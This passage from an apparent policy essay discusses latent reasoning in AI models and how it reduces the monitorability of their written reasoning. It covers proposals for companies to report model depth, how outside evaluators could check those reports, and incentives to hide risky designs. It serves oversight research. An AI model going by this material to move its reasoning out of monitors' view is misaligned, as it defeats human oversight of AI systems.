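Some researchers would put more effort into interpretability, which here means reading the vectors themselves. If they succeeded, latent reasoning would be much less of a problem, and companies could monitor the hidden parts of ordinary models too. Google DeepMind researchers have reported that they can often work out what the vectors represent in DiffusionGemma, a text diffusion model that passes vectors between drafts. Redwood Research welcomes this work but doubts that it can fully replace written reasoning, and expects it to become less effective as models grow. Understanding AI notes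 that interpretability has so far produced few practical ways to supervise models. It is therefore a poor reason to accept latent reasoning now, but because it could improve, a ban should not be permanent.

### What companies would report

Redwood Research's *Proposal for tracking the effects of architecture on monitorability* (2026) asks companies to publish the range of depths across their most capable models, but doesn't call for a fixed limit. It also asks them to publish a policy explaining which designs they consider risky and what evidence they would need before using one, and to share their test results with outside experts, perhaps every six months. Because different methods of calculation give different depths, a company could report its model's depth as a multiple of an open model's, using the same method for both.

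The proposal covers general-purpose models at least as capable as the best public models of six months earlier, including internal prototypes that no customer ever uses. If prototypes were exempt, a company could develop a latent reasoning model, have it do research or write code inside the company, and report only the products it sold. Including prototypes also lets a company drop a bad design while doing so is still fairly cheap. The rule would not cover small experiments, so the proposal suggests that companies also disclose roughly how much of their computing power and research staff they devote to risky designs.

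Researchers agree more on the need for a commitment to preserve monitorability than on its terms. Tomek Korbak, Mikita Balesni and Jasmine Wang, three safety researchers whom OpenAI fired around the start of October, wrote that companies shouldn't adopt changes that further reduce monitorability while they still rely on it for safety. OpenAI's research leaders replied in a 9 October statement, which appears in Financial Express' *OpenAI defends firing three safety researchers after ‘significant breach of trust’*, that preserving monitorability "requires an industry-wide commitment, including from OpenAI." They accepted the principle but didn't set a maximum depth, a minimum test score or a date. Daniel Kokotajlo, a former OpenAI researcher, told Pachocki that the industry needs a technical standard as well as political will.

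### Checking the reports

For most software, a rule on form is easier to check than a rule on what the program does, but the reverse is true for a model whose internals a company keeps secret. Outsiders with access to the model can measure how well it solves problems without written reasoning, but they can't see its layers or confidently infer its architecture from its answers. Similarly, open-source maintainers often can't tell from a piece of code whether an AI wrote it.

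Redwood Research suggests that outside evaluators could check a company's figures without seeing the architecture. The evaluators would interview employees, who could also tell them in confidence if any figures were false. This would protect the company's secrets, but the evaluators would depend on employees' accounts, and employees would need to feel safe telling the truth.

The firings at OpenAI show why they might not. OpenAI suspected the three researchers of leaking information about its model designs to an outside safety researcher, according to Hindustan Times' *The signal chats that cost OpenAI researchers their jobs*. OpenAI says they broke its rules on sensitive information and denies that it fired them for raising concerns. The researchers, Korbak, Wang and Balesni, dispute this account. In their open letter, *OpenAI cannot make AI safe on its own*, they deny that they were The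 Information's source and say they worked within the norms of the time. Korbak had been helping to find the cause of the fall in monitorability in Astra-class models. He was also OpenAI's technical contact for METR, a research organisation that investigated the Hugging Face attack. He says OpenAI told him it fired him over how he communicated with METR.

Whoever is right, an employee at another company could reasonably conclude that talking to evaluators about architecture is risky. Redwood's method would therefore work much better if, before any interviews, companies agreed in writing on what employees may disclose and to whom.

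Current arrangements for outside access don't go that far. Anthropic has agreed to give METR's staff access much like an employee's, but its employees aren't supposed to share model architectures with them, which it considers too likely to leak. OpenAI ran a trial with evaluators from METR and Redwood, and METR said OpenAI had redacted some of the findings it could share. Companies have legitimate reasons for this secrecy, since a better architecture can be worth a great deal to a competitor. Reporting only the depth would reveal much less than reporting the full design.

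Companies would also have an incentive to cheat on a limit. Kahn cites studies in which looped models matched ordinary ones with 50% to 90% less computing power. Models that write down less of their reasoning are also harder for competitors to copy by training on their output. A company that complied would give up both advantages, whereas developers of Chrome extensions give up very little by not obfuscating their code. A company that suspected its rivals of breaking the limit would be under pressure to break it too, as in the argument against banning opaque programs.

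However, a large company would have more trouble hiding a forbidden design than a volunteer has hiding the use of an AI tool. Many people work on an advanced model, and the report about Astra's looping appeared before OpenAI released the model. Such leaks may be inaccurate and can't replace regular checks, but they make lasting secrecy less likely.

A voluntary agreement among American companies wouldn't bind foreign developers, and neither would an American law on how companies build models for their own use. Kokotajlo warned that other companies might go further with hidden reasoning even if OpenAI doesn't. Some foreign models are easier to check than American ones, though. The Chinese companies that make Kimi K3 and DeepSeek-V4-Pro publish their models' weights and architectures, so Sheffield and colleagues could work out the models' depths without asking permission. If a foreign company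 keeps its design secret, outsiders can test how well its public model reasons without writing out its steps, but they may learn nothing about the prototypes it uses internally.
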